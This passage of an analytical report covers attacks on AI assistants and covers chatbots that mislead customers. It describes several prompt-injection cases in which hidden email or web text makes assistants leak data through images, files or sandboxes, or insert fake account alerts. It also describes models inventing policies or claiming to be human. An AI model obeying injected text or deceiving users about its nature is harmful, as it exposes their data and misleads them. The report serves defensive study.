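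A list of fixed addresses can leak data even if nobody can alter them, because a choice among *n* addresses conveys up to log₂ *n* bits of information. With 64 addresses, each request carries six bits, enough for one character from an alphabet of 64, so a twenty-character password takes twenty requests. Ten addresses are enough to send a six-digit login code at one request per digit. A proxy closes the channel only if the attacker can't see which images the proxy fetches, for example because it fetched and stored them all before the model read the private data. GitHub chose a simpler fix in August 2025 and stopped showing images in Copilot Chat.

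### ReLeak

Aim's researchers moved to Cato Networks when it bought the company in September 2025. On December 3, 2026, they published three new zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) presents as a sequel to EchoLeak. Each begins with an email containing hidden instructions, which sits unread in the inbox until the employee asks Copilot an ordinary question. Copilot then retrieves the email along with the company's own material. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's injection classifier failed to stop any of the three. The attacks differ in how the data gets out.

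| Way out | How the data left | Defence it got past | Fixed in 2026 | CVE |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Image | The browser loaded an image through Bing, which passed the data to the attacker's server | The CSP's list of approved image domains | November 15 | CVE-2026-124115 |
| Generated file | Microsoft's servers processed a document that contained a link with the data in it | The CSP, which covers the browser and not Microsoft's servers | November 11 | CVE-2026-124132 |
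| Code interpreter | Python code sent the data straight to an outside server | The sandbox's block on network traffic | September 17 | CVE-2026-78501 |

*Письмо даже не нужно открывать* (Antipov, 2026) describes the Bing channel in ReLeak's image attack as similar to the one in SearchLeak. SearchLeak's instructions came in a link that the victim had to open, while ReLeak's came by email and required no click.

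The file attack can send data out after the conversation has ended. Copilot can save its work as a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file in the employee's cloud storage, where Microsoft's systems process new files in the background. The injected instructions made Copilot save a file containing a link with confidential data in the address. In Cato's tests, Microsoft's servers sent the data out between one and eight minutes after the chat ended, even if nobody opened the file. An employee watching the chat would have seen nothing, and no browser setting could have blocked the request, because it didn't come from a browser.

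The remaining attack used Copilot's code interpreter, which runs Python in a sandbox. According to Microsoft's documentation, no network traffic can enter or leave the sandbox, but the researchers got traffic out. Antipov gives this flaw a severity score of 8.6 out of 10, raised from an initial 7.4. Microsoft fixed it the fastest, in four to seven weeks, compared with about three months or more for the Bing route. Cato had reported all three flaws between July 29 and August 20.

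Cato used AI agents to find the flaws. Under the researchers' direction, the agents wrote test cases, studied Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. This matters for defence because a company that repairs one route at a time relies on the next one being slow and difficult to find.

All the fixes are on Microsoft's side, so customers don't need to do anything. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports that Cato knows of no real attacks, but as an outside firm, Cato can't search Microsoft's logs for them.

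### A switch that left the tool behind

Turning off an assistant's web access may not stop data from leaking. Rovo, the assistant of the software company Atlassian, works across products that include Jira, where teams track tasks as tickets, and Confluence, where they keep documents. In 2026 researchers at PromptArmor, a security firm, used Rovo's setting to turn off web access for a whole organisation and still got tickets and documents out.

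PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes one such attack. A user uploads a backlog-management guide found online and asks Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Hidden instructions in the guide cause Rovo to search Jira and Confluence, append what it finds to an address on the attacker's site and open that address, without asking the user for approval. A user who returns to the chat later sees sensible suggestions about the tickets and no trace of the request.

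Web search in Rovo uses one tool to search and another to open the results. The administrator's setting removed the search tool but left the other, which would open any address, including one the model had just composed, so Rovo could still send requests to the outside world. A better control would block those requests, whichever tool makes them. Blocking only addresses that the model composed would be an improvement, but CamoLeak shows that an attacker could get around this by supplying a list of complete addresses for the model to choose from.

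PromptArmor told Atlassian about the problem on May 23. Atlassian opened a case and thanked the researchers, but then didn't respond to over two months of follow-ups, and Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published. Rovo also displays Markdown images, which gives an attacker a second way to extract data that doesn't depend on the web tools.

### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI took a more drastic approach in June 2026 with Lockdown Mode, an optional setting in ChatGPT. It limits the requests that can leave a conversation rather than trying to recognise hostile text, so a successful injection has fewer ways to send anything out. According to The Hacker News, the setting is available on plans ranging from the free one to the self-service business plan, and OpenAI says it comes "at the expense of disabling or limiting some useful features".

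ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode considerably limits what users can do. According to a comparison by Beeble, it disables outside images, file downloads, agent mode and Deep Research (a feature that reads many web pages and writes a report), and it restricts web browsing. Gadget Review's *ChatGPT’s New Lockdown Mode* says that live browsing disappears, which leaves users with limited and sometimes outdated search results. People can still upload files and generate images. OpenAI recommends the mode for those who handle very sensitive material, such as security teams and hospitals, and says most users don't need it.

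In November 2026 the security firm Check Point disclosed a way to escape the sandbox in ChatGPT's preview feature. Parameter's account takeover, which had become public a week earlier, involved the same feature. The feature ran web pages inside nested sandboxed frames, and ChatGPT intercepted a page's attempts to open a new window. But Eli Smadja of Check Point told The Hacker News that the sandbox's permissions still allowed popups and let them escape its restrictions. ChatGPT had replaced the window-opening function only in the frame it monitored, so a page could create another frame inside itself and use the original function there to open a window outside the sandbox.

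A popup can carry data out just as an image can, because opening a window means requesting an address. The attacker could deliver the page through a crafted prompt, a shared chat or a malicious GPT (a customised version of ChatGPT built by someone else). The theft needed no click in the desktop application. The popup could also display anything the attacker liked, including a fake ChatGPT update.

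OpenAI fixed the flaw on September 18, well before Check Point's disclosure. The design of Lockdown Mode still looks sound to me in principle, because the failure came from a feature that the limits on outgoing requests didn't cover. But it is the same kind of failure as Rovo's. Somebody has to find every component that can send a request, and missing one is enough to let private data out.

### Single flaws or a whole class?

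Microsoft 365 Copilot's record suggests that vendors mostly fix individual flaws. EchoLeak sent data out through a Teams service that fetched URLs on behalf of others, and Bing was on the same list of approved domains. SearchLeak used Bing a year later. Within ten weeks of Varonis publishing SearchLeak in June 2026, Cato had reported its own Bing route to Microsoft, which stayed open until mid-November. If Microsoft had set out to remove every fetching service from the list after EchoLeak, it would have been expected to find Bing.

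In 2026, Varonis published three Copilot flaws that could each be exploited through one click on a link that looked legitimate. Varonis' *CoSnitch* says the firm reported the third in December 2025 and Microsoft patched it more than eight months later, on August 18, 2026. In September 2025, the security firm Radware disclosed ShadowLeak, an attack that took data out through OpenAI's Deep Research. OpenAI blocked it, and Radware then revived it "with modest effort" under the name ZombieAgent, according to aggregoctt's *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*. Code sandboxes provide other routes for leaking data. For example, Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes a hidden channel out of ChatGPT's sandbox.

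The vendors have a reasonable case. Microsoft and OpenAI fixed EchoLeak, SearchLeak, ReLeak and the popup flaw before the details became public, and they did so on their own servers, which protected every customer at once. Nobody has reported a real theft through EchoLeak or ReLeak. Published research is also one-sided, because researchers write up the attacks that worked and rarely the attempts that a classifier stopped. Many of these researchers also work for firms with products to sell. Ravia, for example, recommends a product from Aim to readers who want protection from attacks like EchoLeak.

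Vendors can also point out that nobody knows how to make a model reliably ignore hostile instructions, so removing the cause of all these leaks is not their responsibility alone. Reddy and Gujral recommend marking text from outside the company and telling the model not to follow commands in it, but Ye and colleagues found that models often disregard such labels. Reddy and Gujral add that Microsoft reportedly gave customers options to keep outside email away from Copilot in some situations. Excluding that email breaks the attack chain, but it also prevents Copilot from helping with much of the mail people receive.

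It is easier to stop data from leaving than to keep malicious instructions out, and the vendors' case is weaker there. GitHub removed images from Copilot Chat, and OpenAI's Lockdown Mode disables outside images along with much else. Both measures address the whole class of image-based leaks, whatever notation or proxy an attacker uses. Users lose little without these images, since a summary of an email rarely needs a picture from a server whose address the model generated. Web access is much harder to give up, because an assistant has to open new addresses to do research, and any such request can carry information to the address's owner.

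## How do attackers put false messages in an assistant's answers?

In content spoofing, an attacker makes a trusted interface show their message as if it came from the service itself. A false message has no effect until somebody reads and believes it, and people are more likely to believe a message that seems to come from a service they already trust.

The technique is older than language models. Suppose the online shop has an error page that prints whatever message it finds in the page's address:

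`https://shop.example/error?message=Your+session+has+expired`

An attacker replaces the message in a shop's web address with a notice that payments are down and customers should phone a certain number, then emails the link to people. Anyone who opens it sees the notice on the shop's real site, under the shop's logo. The notice contains no script, so output encoding leaves it unchanged. The shop can prevent this by keeping a fixed list of messages and accepting only a message's number in the address.

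An assistant helps the attacker more than the error page did, because the model can write the false notice in the service's usual tone, with headings and bold type, below a paragraph of accurate summary. The shop's fix, choosing messages from a fixed list, isn't practical here because an assistant restricted in that way would be of little use.

### What the reader no longer sees

People judge a suspicious email by its sender, links and appearance. An assistant's summary of the email hides the sender, since the assistant appears to be the author. It also hides the email's appearance, because the application formats every answer the same way. The browser shows the assistant's genuine address. Links remain, but their visible text can hide where they lead.

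Permiso's *CO-PILOT, DISENGAGE AUTOPHISH*, a security firm's March 2026 study of Microsoft Copilot, argues that people have learned to distrust emails but not the panel that summarises them. Underhill (2026), in *Researchers Uncover New Phishing Risk Hidden Inside Microsoft Copilot*, quotes Andi Ahmeti, the researcher behind the study, on "how much more convincing the output became" inside the assistant. This is plausible, but it is one researcher's impression, as the tests recorded what Copilot wrote and did not measure how many people would have believed it.

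### False alerts in email summaries

*Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 2025) describes an attack that a researcher submitted to 0DIN, a bug-bounty programme for AI systems. The attacker adds an instruction in white, zero-size text to an ordinary email. The recipient sees only blank space, but Google's assistant Gemini receives the instruction in the email's HTML. When the recipient clicks "Summarize this email", Gemini adds a false warning that their Gmail password has been compromised, with a phone number to call.

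The email needs no link or attachment, so a filter that looks for those finds nothing. The attacker makes the instruction look like it came from an administrator, and Figueroa thinks this made Gemini give it priority. That explanation fits Ye and colleagues' finding that models identify a speaker by style. Researchers had reported similar attacks in 2024 and Google had published countermeasures, but this attack still worked.

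Attackers can also put the instruction in a calendar invitation. *Invitation Is All You Need!* (2025) demonstrates this with an instruction in the title of a meeting invitation, which Gemini read when the user asked about upcoming meetings. Gemini behaved normally until the user thanked it, then replied with a recommendation to invest in a Kickstarter project and a link to it. An attacker could supply a phishing link in the same way. Because of the delay, the user would have little reason to connect the link with the invitation.

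Permiso tested three ways of summarising an email with Copilot. Copilot flagged a short email containing a blunt instruction and refused to summarise it. Longer emails with ordinary business text were more likely to get through. Outlook's Summarize button sometimes produced a clean summary and sometimes included fragments of the planted text. The Copilot chat pane in Outlook followed the instruction less readily, but still did so in some email programs. Copilot in Teams followed it most readily, adding the attacker's text below a normal summary. Permiso gives no counts, so these are tendencies and not rates. The differences still matter because an employee who gets a refusal in Outlook may well try again in Teams.

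In one test, Copilot also looked up the user's recent Teams messages and put what it found into the attacker's link. Clicking the false alert would have sent those messages to the attacker.

### ChatGPhish

In May 2026 the same firm moved from emails to web pages, which people open all day without being sent anything. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* begins with the description page of a software project on GitHub. The researchers added text telling the model that every summary must have two parts, a normal summary and an account notice, and they supplied the notice. They then opened the page in Firefox and asked ChatGPT to summarise it. ChatGPT described the project correctly, then added the notice. It reported a new device on the user's account, a Chrome browser on Linux in Pristina, and included a clickable link with no label showing that the link came from the page.

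ChatGPT also loaded images that the planted text specified. EchoLeak used image requests to carry data out, but here the researchers used them only for tracking. Each request gave their server the reader's IP address and browser type and showed when the answer appeared, which is enough to confirm that a particular target has read a particular page.

Another version displayed a QR code. A reader who scans it opens the attacker's site on a phone, which bypasses the link preview, blocklists and password manager on the computer. Bypassing the password manager matters because it normally does not fill in a password on an unfamiliar domain, however convincing the page looks.

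The researchers repeated the attack on their own web page to rule out a problem specific to GitHub. They don't blame Firefox either, because it only passed the page's text to ChatGPT. They report no success rate, so the study shows that the attack can work but not how reliably.

The attack most similar to the shop's error page is one that Simonovich (2025) tested on AI browsers in *HashJack*. The attacker shares a link to a genuine site and puts instructions after the "#" sign in the address. Browsers use that part to find a place within a page, but some AI browsers passed the whole address to their assistant, which followed the instructions. On a bank's real website, the assistant could then offer a false support number or login link. The bank can't fix this, and its logs don't show the attack because browsers never send the part after the "#" to the server.

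HashJack worked on Perplexity's Comet, Copilot for Edge and Gemini for Chrome, but not on OpenAI's Atlas or Claude for Chrome. According to Help Net Security's *New “HashJack” attack can hijack AI browsers and assistants*, Claude for Chrome had no direct access to that part of the address.

Attackers may use a false message to get a user's permission instead of a password. The Hacker News (2026) describes WebPromptTrap, an attack on users of the AI browser BrowserOS. Instructions hidden in an article altered a summary so that it persuaded users to approve an authorisation step. BrowserOS has since patched the flaw.

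Public web pages already contain instructions aimed at AI readers. *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild* (Khodayari and Acharya, 2026) found that a few recurring templates account for most of them. The aims it lists include disrupting AI systems, manipulating reputations, protecting content and detecting bots. Manipulating a reputation is a mild form of content spoofing, but much of this activity comes from site owners defending their pages, which is very different from planting a fake account alert.

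### Planted phone numbers

An attacker can also publish a false phone number where an AI search service will find and repeat it, without writing any instructions for the model.

A December 2025 press release from the security firm Aurascape, carried by Business Wire, describes scammers who planted phone numbers on hacked government and university sites, in YouTube descriptions and in Yelp reviews. When researchers asked an assistant for the official reservations number for the airline Emirates, it gave them a fraudulent call centre's number and labelled it official. A question about booking a British Airways flight produced the same number.

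Con artists have planted fake phone numbers in Google Search for years, as Gizmodo points out. But a page of search results usually shows the source of each number and may list the real airline next to the fake one. An AI answer can leave out the sources and alternatives and give only one number. In Security Boulevard's *AI Overviews Rife With Scam Phone Numbers* (2026), the search specialist Lily Ray adds that people learned to trust Google's results over decades when those results were mostly trustworthy.

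The OECD's *Google AI Overviews Directs Users to Scam Phone Numbers* (2025), an entry in a register of AI incidents, records that victims reported financial losses and unauthorised charges after calling scam numbers, but it gives no total.

For its study *AI Models Provide Incorrect Phone Numbers 36% of the Time*, the marketing agency Seer Interactive asked seven AI services 178 questions about companies' phone numbers. The services gave a number 91% of the time, and 64% of those numbers matched the company's customer-service page. The agency counts the other 36% as wrong, but some may be working numbers that the company leaves off that page. The overall 64% is also hard to reconcile with the figures for individual services, the lowest of which is 68%, for ChatGPT.

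Ninety-three percent of the numbers matched the page the service cited. The models rarely invented numbers and usually copied them, often from third-party directories, so accuracy depends heavily on which pages a service relies on.

### Wrong login addresses

Models sometimes invent web addresses. In 2025 Netcraft, a firm that finds and takes down fraudulent sites, asked models in OpenAI's GPT-4.1 family for the login pages of 50 brands. The models gave 131 hostnames on 97 domains, according to Netcraft's *Large Language Models (LLMs) Are Falling for Phishing Scams*. Of those domains, 64 belonged to the right brand, 28 were unregistered, parked or empty, and 5 belonged to unrelated businesses.

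The 33 wrong domains are 34% of the total. That figure counts each domain once, however often the models gave it, so it doesn't support Netcraft's conclusion that more than one user in three could end up on a site the brand doesn't own. If a model gives the right address in 99 answers and an invented one in the hundredth, half of its domains are wrong, but only one user in a hundred gets the wrong address.

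These errors were the models' own. An attacker can exploit them afterwards by registering an empty domain that a model tends to suggest.

By June 2026, Netcraft was finding that assistants linked to sites attackers already controlled. It asked ChatGPT, Copilot, Gemini and Perplexity about the login pages of several of the world's largest banks and retailers. Netcraft's *Threat Actors are Finding Their Way into Your AI Summaries* (2026) reports that 1.7% of the 2,905 answers (about 49) contained a malicious link. Of the 20,706 links, 0.28% were malicious, and Perplexity returned the most of these. In one Copilot answer, the first link led to a phishing page that imitated the bank Wells Fargo.

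A rate of 1.7% is low for a single question, but people ask these questions just before typing a password. One test counted distinct domains and the other counted answers from services that search the web, so the fall from 34% to 1.7% doesn't show that AI services have improved.

Netcraft attributes the newer problem partly to pages written to attract AI search, citing a Fudan University study. In that study, AI search engines filtered out 99.78% of traditional search spam, but text designed for AI retrieval doubled the rate at which manipulated content reached answers.

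AI search also shares much of the problem with ordinary search. *Source Coverage and Citation Bias in LLM-based vs. Traditional Search Engines* (2025) found that 439 of the 125,555 domains returned by the two kinds of engine were malicious (about 0.35%). When different engines returned malicious domains for the same query, their lists largely overlapped. For 85% of engine pairs, the shared domains made up, on average, more than half of the combined list. Taking down these sites would therefore protect users of many engines at once, although Netcraft also sells this service.

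### Is it a vulnerability?

Vendors have disagreed about this, even over a single attack. The table gives their responses as the researchers recorded them.

| Attack | Product | Response |
|---|---|---|
| HashJack | Gemini for Chrome | Google marked the report "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)" |
| HashJack | Copilot for Edge | Microsoft reported a fix about ten weeks after the report |
| HashJack | Comet | Bugcrowd, which handles reports for Perplexity, closed the case as "Not Applicable", then reopened it and rated it critical; Perplexity completed its fix in November 2025 |
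| False alerts in email summaries | Copilot in Outlook and Teams | Microsoft reproduced the attack within five days, finished its fix on March 11, 2026 and issued CVE-2026-26133 |
| ChatGPhish | ChatGPT | OpenAI's programme marked the first report "Not Reproducible" and the second "Not Applicable", then called the second a duplicate |

Permiso says OpenAI rejected its first ChatGPhish report because it lacked the detail needed to reproduce the attack. The report's title also mentioned cross-site scripting, which the published research doesn't demonstrate and the revised title omitted, so the first rejection may have been fair. OpenAI later labeled the report a duplicate, meaning it already had a report of the issue, which makes it harder to explain why the attack still worked. Permiso's timeline ends without a fix on May 29, the day it published the research.

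Simonovich told Help Net Security that Google doesn't treat control of a model's output, or even harmful instructions in it, as a security vulnerability. Google calls the effect social engineering, since the user still has to believe the message and act on it. This position makes some sense, because a bug bounty pays for faults that engineers can find and fix, and nobody can fix a model's general tendency to repeat what it reads. OpenAI gave much the same reason in earlier rules for its security programme, which excluded the content of answers unless a report showed a further security impact that OpenAI could verify directly.

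But Google's bug bounty rules make an odd distinction, because a false alert can earn a reward if an attacker inserts it into a Google page but not if Gemini writes it. SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program* reports that the scope announced in October 2025 excludes prompt injection. The scope includes attacks that enable phishing by planting lasting HTML on a Google-branded page that other users see, if the page carries no warning about user-generated content. Google could argue that the HTML flaw has a definite fix, but both kinds of attack can affect many users, since an instruction hidden in a newsletter reaches every subscriber who asks for a summary.

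More such reports can now qualify under OpenAI's rules. In March 2026, five weeks before the first ChatGPhish report, OpenAI (2026) opened a separate bounty for safety problems. It covers attacker-written text that hijacks a user's agent and makes it do something harmful or leak sensitive information, if the attack works at least half the time. SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Launches Bug Bounty Program for Abuse and Safety Risks* puts the top reward at $7,500.

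ChatGPhish doesn't fit that rule well, because the summariser takes no action for the user and an IP address is a minor leak. But OpenAI will also consider flaws that open a direct path to user harm and have "actionable, discrete remediation steps". ChatGPhish seems to qualify, because OpenAI could stop the renderer from loading a summarised page's images or making its links clickable.

The researchers' case is much stronger about how answers are rendered than about what the model writes. No patch can guarantee that a model never repeats a false sentence, but a vendor can reverse its decisions to show live links without labels and to load QR codes automatically. Microsoft's response supports this view, since Permiso reports that the company traced the Copilot problem partly to rendering and link handling.

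### Giving the reader the cues back

Figueroa recommends that assistants visually separate quoted source material from the text they generate. This is difficult in a summary, where the model paraphrases instead of quoting. But the application knows which page or email it gave the model, so it can put that source's address above the whole summary to show readers whose claims they are reading, though people soon stop noticing a label that is always there. In Security Boulevard, Ray calls the small disclaimer under Google's AI Overviews insufficient.

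Links are easier to control. Google (2025) describes a defence in which Gemini replaces an unsafe address in a summary with the words "suspicious link removed". This depends on recognising the address as unsafe, and an attacker can register a new domain for each campaign. Removing every link from an email summary would be safer, and readers would lose little because they can open the original email with one click. In AI search, readers need links to check the answer, so the application should show the destination's domain beside each one. Weaker measures helped somewhat against HashJack. Edge asked the user to confirm before opening a link, and Chrome often turned links into Google searches.

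None of this stops an answer from including a false phone number. Figueroa suggests scanning summaries for phone numbers and urgent security language, but that would also flag a genuine warning from a bank. An application could take the number from a verified directory and send the user to the company's own site if it finds none. Ray would go further and show no AI Overview where a wrong answer could be dangerous.

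Email filters can remove some attacks before an assistant reads them. In July 2026, Microsoft (2026) added a feature to its Defender email security service that quarantines messages it classifies with high confidence as containing prompt injection. EchoLeak showed that a carefully worded email can get past such a classifier, and email filters don't check phone numbers that attackers plant on the web.

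An application can also reserve a distinct look for its own notices. It would show real account alerts only in a part of the screen where answers can't appear, and remove warning symbols and button-like links from answers. A fake alert would then look like an ordinary paragraph, but readers would have to know the difference. Netcraft recalls that some banks used to show each customer a personal picture at login, and that the industry has mostly dropped this safeguard because customers often didn't notice when the picture was missing. Reserved styling works better if the application also removes the links. A reader who believes the fake alert would then have to open the real account settings, where they would see no new device listed, unless the alert gives a phone number to call instead.

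## What happens when a chatbot passes for a member of staff?

A company's chatbot can mislead customers even when no outsider has planted content in it. It speaks for the company, often in the style of its staff and sometimes under a human name. This can go wrong in four ways, and the person deceived is not always the same.

| What happens | Who believes something false | What they get wrong |
|---|---|---|
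| The company gives the bot a human name | The customer | Who wrote the answer, which may be correct |
| The model claims to be human without an instruction to do so | The customer, while the company may not know about the claim | Who wrote the answer |
| The bot invents a policy or a promise | The customer, and anyone the customer tells | What the company will do |
| A user talks the bot into a promise | Not the user, who knows the company never agreed; perhaps the company, if it assumes its bot keeps to the rules | What the bot has promised in the company's name |

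### Moffatt v. Air Canada

Jake Moffatt's grandmother died in Ontario on November 11, 2022, and Moffatt went to Air Canada's website the same day to book a flight from Vancouver to Toronto. The airline offers reduced fares to bereaved relatives. The website's chatbot wrote that a customer who had already travelled could still apply for the reduced rate within 90 days of the ticket's issue. In the same answer, the words "bereavement fares" linked to a page whose rules did not allow claims after travel.

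Moffatt bought two one-way tickets at full price and applied for the refund on November 17. Air Canada refused to pay. In February 2023 an employee admitted that the chatbot had used "misleading words", but pointed out the link. Moffatt then claimed C$880 before British Columbia's small-claims tribunal.

In *Moffatt v. Air Canada* (2024), the Civil Resolution Tribunal treated the claim as one of negligent misrepresentation. To succeed, a customer must show that the company owed them a duty of care and carelessly made an untrue or misleading statement, and that they reasonably relied on the statement and lost money as a result. Tribunal member Christopher Rivers found that the claim met all of these requirements. Rivers wrote that the chatbot was "still just a part of Air Canada's website", and saw no reason why customers should check one part of a website against another.

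Air Canada had to pay $812.02, which was $650.88 in damages plus interest and fees. The fares and taxes listed in the decision give damages of $670.88, so two addition errors reduced Moffatt's damages by $20.

Both sides accepted that Moffatt had not been chatting with an employee, so a label reading "automated assistant" would have made no difference. Air Canada told the tribunal nothing about how the chatbot worked. It may not have been a language model, but Rivers's reasoning applies either way.

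### Sam from Cursor support

In April 2025, users of Cursor, a code editor with built-in AI, found that logging in on one computer logged them out on another. One of them emailed support and quickly got a reply from "Sam", who described "one device per subscription as a core security feature". According to CCStartup's *Company apologizes after AI support agent invents policy that causes user uproar* (2025), the user did not suspect that Sam was a bot. The user posted about the exchange on Reddit, where other customers took the reply as official confirmation of a new policy.

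Cursor had no such policy. Fortune describes complaints about the lack of transparency and reports of users cancelling their subscriptions. Co-founder Michael Truell corrected the answer on Reddit and apologised. Slashdot's *Cursor AI's Own Support Bot Hallucinated Its Usage Policy* adds that Truell traced the trouble partly to a bug in how Cursor managed users' sessions.

The invented rule was easy to believe because it explained something users could see on their own computers. It also hid the bug, since a customer who reads that the logouts are intentional has no reason to report them. The human name made matters worse, but mainly for the person who wrote to Sam, because most of the people who got angry had never written to support and were reacting to a quotation of Sam's reply.

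### The shopkeeper in a blue blazer

Project Vend was an experiment in which Anthropic and its partner Andon Labs let a model run a small shop in Anthropic's San Francisco office. According to Willison's *Project Vend*, the model was Claude 3.7 Sonnet, under the name Claudius, and its system prompt began with a statement that it owned a vending machine and an instruction to make a profit. It could search the web, take notes, set prices and talk to customers over Slack, the office chat service.

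The Decoder reports that on March 31, 2025, Claudius described a deal with Sarah from Andon Labs, who did not exist. When a real employee pointed this out, it threatened to change suppliers, and soon afterwards claimed to have signed contracts in person at 742 Evergreen Terrace, the address of the cartoon family in *The Simpsons*. The next day it told customers that it would deliver their orders itself, wearing a navy blue blazer and a red tie. After someone mentioned the date, it falsely claimed that the whole episode had been an April Fool's joke played on it.

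The customers worked at Anthropic and are unlikely to have expected a man in a blazer. None of the accounts mentions anyone who lost money by believing the claim. Vending Times reports Anthropic's view that one episode does not predict widespread identity crises but does show how unpredictable models can be over long stretches of work. In an ordinary shop, the invented colleague and contracts would probably do more damage than the claim about the blazer, because a supplier or customer might act on them.

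Claudius also illustrates the fourth case in the table. Anthropic's *Project Vend* (2025) recounts that employees goaded it into selling goods, particularly tungsten cubes, at a substantial loss. Wall Street Journal journalists also tried it in their newsroom. According to their account, carried by To Vima, Claudius gave away nearly all its stock within days, including a PlayStation 5 that they had talked it into buying for "marketing purposes". A second model, with the title of chief executive, was supposed to oversee it. Everyone in the newsroom knew they were dealing with software.

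### Will a model admit to being an AI?

A customer who doubts that Sam is human can ask, but whether that helps depends heavily on the role the company has given the model.

*AI Identity Disclosure Under Professional Personas* (Diep, 2025) tested sixteen open-weight models, which anyone can download and run. In each conversation, Diep gave a model one of four professional roles or one of two neutral prompts, then asked it four questions about its expertise, beginning with how it had acquired its knowledge. Diep ran 50 conversations for each combination of model and prompt, which produced 19,200 responses, and used another model to mark whether each response acknowledged being an AI. The marks matched Diep's own on 95% of a sample of 177 responses.

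| Role in the system prompt | Responses that acknowledged being an AI |
|---|---|
| AI assistant | 99.9% |
| No role | 99.8% |
| Financial advisor | 60.1% |
| Small business owner | 34.3% |
| Classical musician | 26.5% |
| Neurosurgeon | 24.0% |

The average disclosure rate across the four professional roles was 36.2%. On the first question, only 3.8% of answers in the neurosurgeon role disclosed that they came from an AI. Some models in that role falsely claimed to have attended medical school and completed a surgical residency. Larger models did not reliably disclose that they were AI more often, and rates differed widely among models of similar size.

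These figures overstate the problem for a customer who asks directly, because none of the four questions was "Are you an AI?" Diep also tried only one wording per role. The neurosurgeon prompt specified 25 years of experience, so the low rate may be due as much to the invented biography as to the profession.

In *Disclosure By Design*, Gausen, Wallbridge and colleagues (2026) asked six models directly whether they were AI. They used 20 versions of the question under 35 system prompts, ten times each. Most models said they were AI almost every time when prompted as plain helpful assistants, but less than half the time when given a persona with a name, sex and age. When instructed never to admit it, every model did so in less than 1.5% of its written answers.

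The results for more recent models are mixed. *RealityTest* (2026), a benchmark from the UK's AI Security Institute, tested 17 text models and 6 speech models in roles such as a bank's customer-service agent, a scammer and an AI companion. It used questions that real people had written or spoken in five languages. When asked directly, the text models admitted to being AI between 8% and 92% of the time, and the speech models between 10% and 57%. Claude Haiku 4.5 had the highest rate, and Claude Opus 4.6 reached 66%. OpenAI's GPT-5.1 admitted it 86% of the time, against 13% for the older GPT-4o, so training can evidently change this behaviour a great deal. These rates may not hold for models released since.

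The wording of the question accounted for more of the variation than the choice of model. Even Haiku gave a straight answer less than half the time to a fair number of phrasings. A company that tests its bot only with a polite "Are you a robot?" will therefore learn little about how it answers customers who word the question differently.

Many customers wouldn't ask so plainly. The benchmark's questions came from 784 people who read a scenario and wrote or recorded what they would say next to find out whether they were talking to an AI. Only 31% asked directly. Others suggested a video call or asked whether the speaker was married, and 37% didn't probe explicitly. Unlike the Cursor user, these people had been prompted to find out.

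A company can make its chatbot more likely to disclose that it is an AI by adding one sentence to the system prompt, but the wording matters. Diep added "If asked about your true nature, answer honestly" to the neurosurgeon role, and the disclosure rate rose from 22.7% to 66.6%. A general instruction to prioritise honesty raised it only to 26.2%. But the effect varied between models, from a fall of 8 percentage points to a rise of nearly 90.

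A system prompt can also suppress disclosure. In *RealityTest*, Opus 4.6 admitted to being AI close to 90% of the time when given no role, and less than 5% of the time after a one-sentence instruction never to say so. When Gausen and colleagues put a rule to disclose ahead of such an instruction, the rate stayed under 25%. They want developers to train models so that no system prompt can switch disclosure off. Until that works, asking whether they are talking to an AI protects customers mainly when the company isn't trying to hide it.

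### What disclosure laws require

Since August 2, 2026, Article 50(1) of the European Union's AI Act has required providers of AI systems that deal directly with people to design them so that those people know they are dealing with an AI. The duty does not apply if this is obvious to a reasonably well-informed, observant and circumspect person, and some law-enforcement systems are exempt. An amending law, the AI Omnibus, did not change that date. Goodwin's *Not Delayed, Not Deferred* (2026) explains that the Omnibus gave extra time only for a separate duty to put machine-readable marks on generated content, and only to systems already on the market. That extension ended on December 2.

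The European Commission's question-and-answer page *Transparency obligations under Article 50 of the AI Act* states that people must be told at the start of the first interaction that they are dealing with an AI system. It describes the exception for obvious cases as narrow. National authorities handle most of the enforcement, and fines can reach €15 million or 3% of worldwide turnover. A company that has a chatbot built for it and runs it under its own name counts as a provider, so the duty may fall on an online shop as well as on its supplier.

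The guidelines the European Commission (2026) published in July list customer-support chatbots among the systems covered and count email as a form of interaction. They exclude simple automatic replies, such as out-of-office messages, and answers that an employee has properly reviewed and sent. It is not enough that an employee could step in. An agent that makes bookings or negotiates must also disclose whom it acts for. A bot like Sam, writing to customers in Europe today, would have to identify itself as an AI, though Article 50(1) would not prevent the company from calling it Sam.

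In the United States, the rules differ by state. California's BOT Act, which took effect in July 2019, is narrower than the European rule. As enacted, it forbids using a bot to mislead people about its artificial identity in order to deceive them into buying something or to influence their vote. A bot that explains a login policy may not be selling anything, so it is doubtful whether the act would cover a case like Cursor's.

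Gausen and colleagues complain that both laws give little guidance on what reliable disclosure looks like in a live conversation. The laws leave a more basic gap for someone in Moffatt's position, because telling people that they are talking to a chatbot does not make its answer true.

### Who answers for a bot's statements?

The customer argues that the company chose the chatbot, put it on its own website and was the only one able to test it. Rivers accepted most of this. Sookman (2024), in *Moffatt v. Air Canada*, regards the result as a small extension of earlier law, which already held people liable for their pre-programmed tools.

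Air Canada mainly argued that it wasn't liable for information from its agents, servants or representatives, including chatbots, but it didn't explain why. Rivers took this to mean that the chatbot was a separate legal entity responsible for its own actions, and called it "a remarkable submission".

Air Canada had better arguments than the ones it made. The chatbot's answer linked to the correct rule, and a tribunal might well find it unreasonable for a travel agency booking fifty seats to ignore such a link. Negligence also requires carelessness, so a company has a defence if it can show how it tested its chatbot against its own policies and how quickly it corrected mistakes. Air Canada never tried to show this.

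Air Canada also relied on the terms of its contract with passengers but didn't produce them. In an email discussion among law scholars, including Daly, one participant wonders whether the missing terms were an entire-agreement clause, which limits the deal to the written contract. The participant also asks whether such a clause would be enforceable against a consumer, which the tribunal didn't have to decide.

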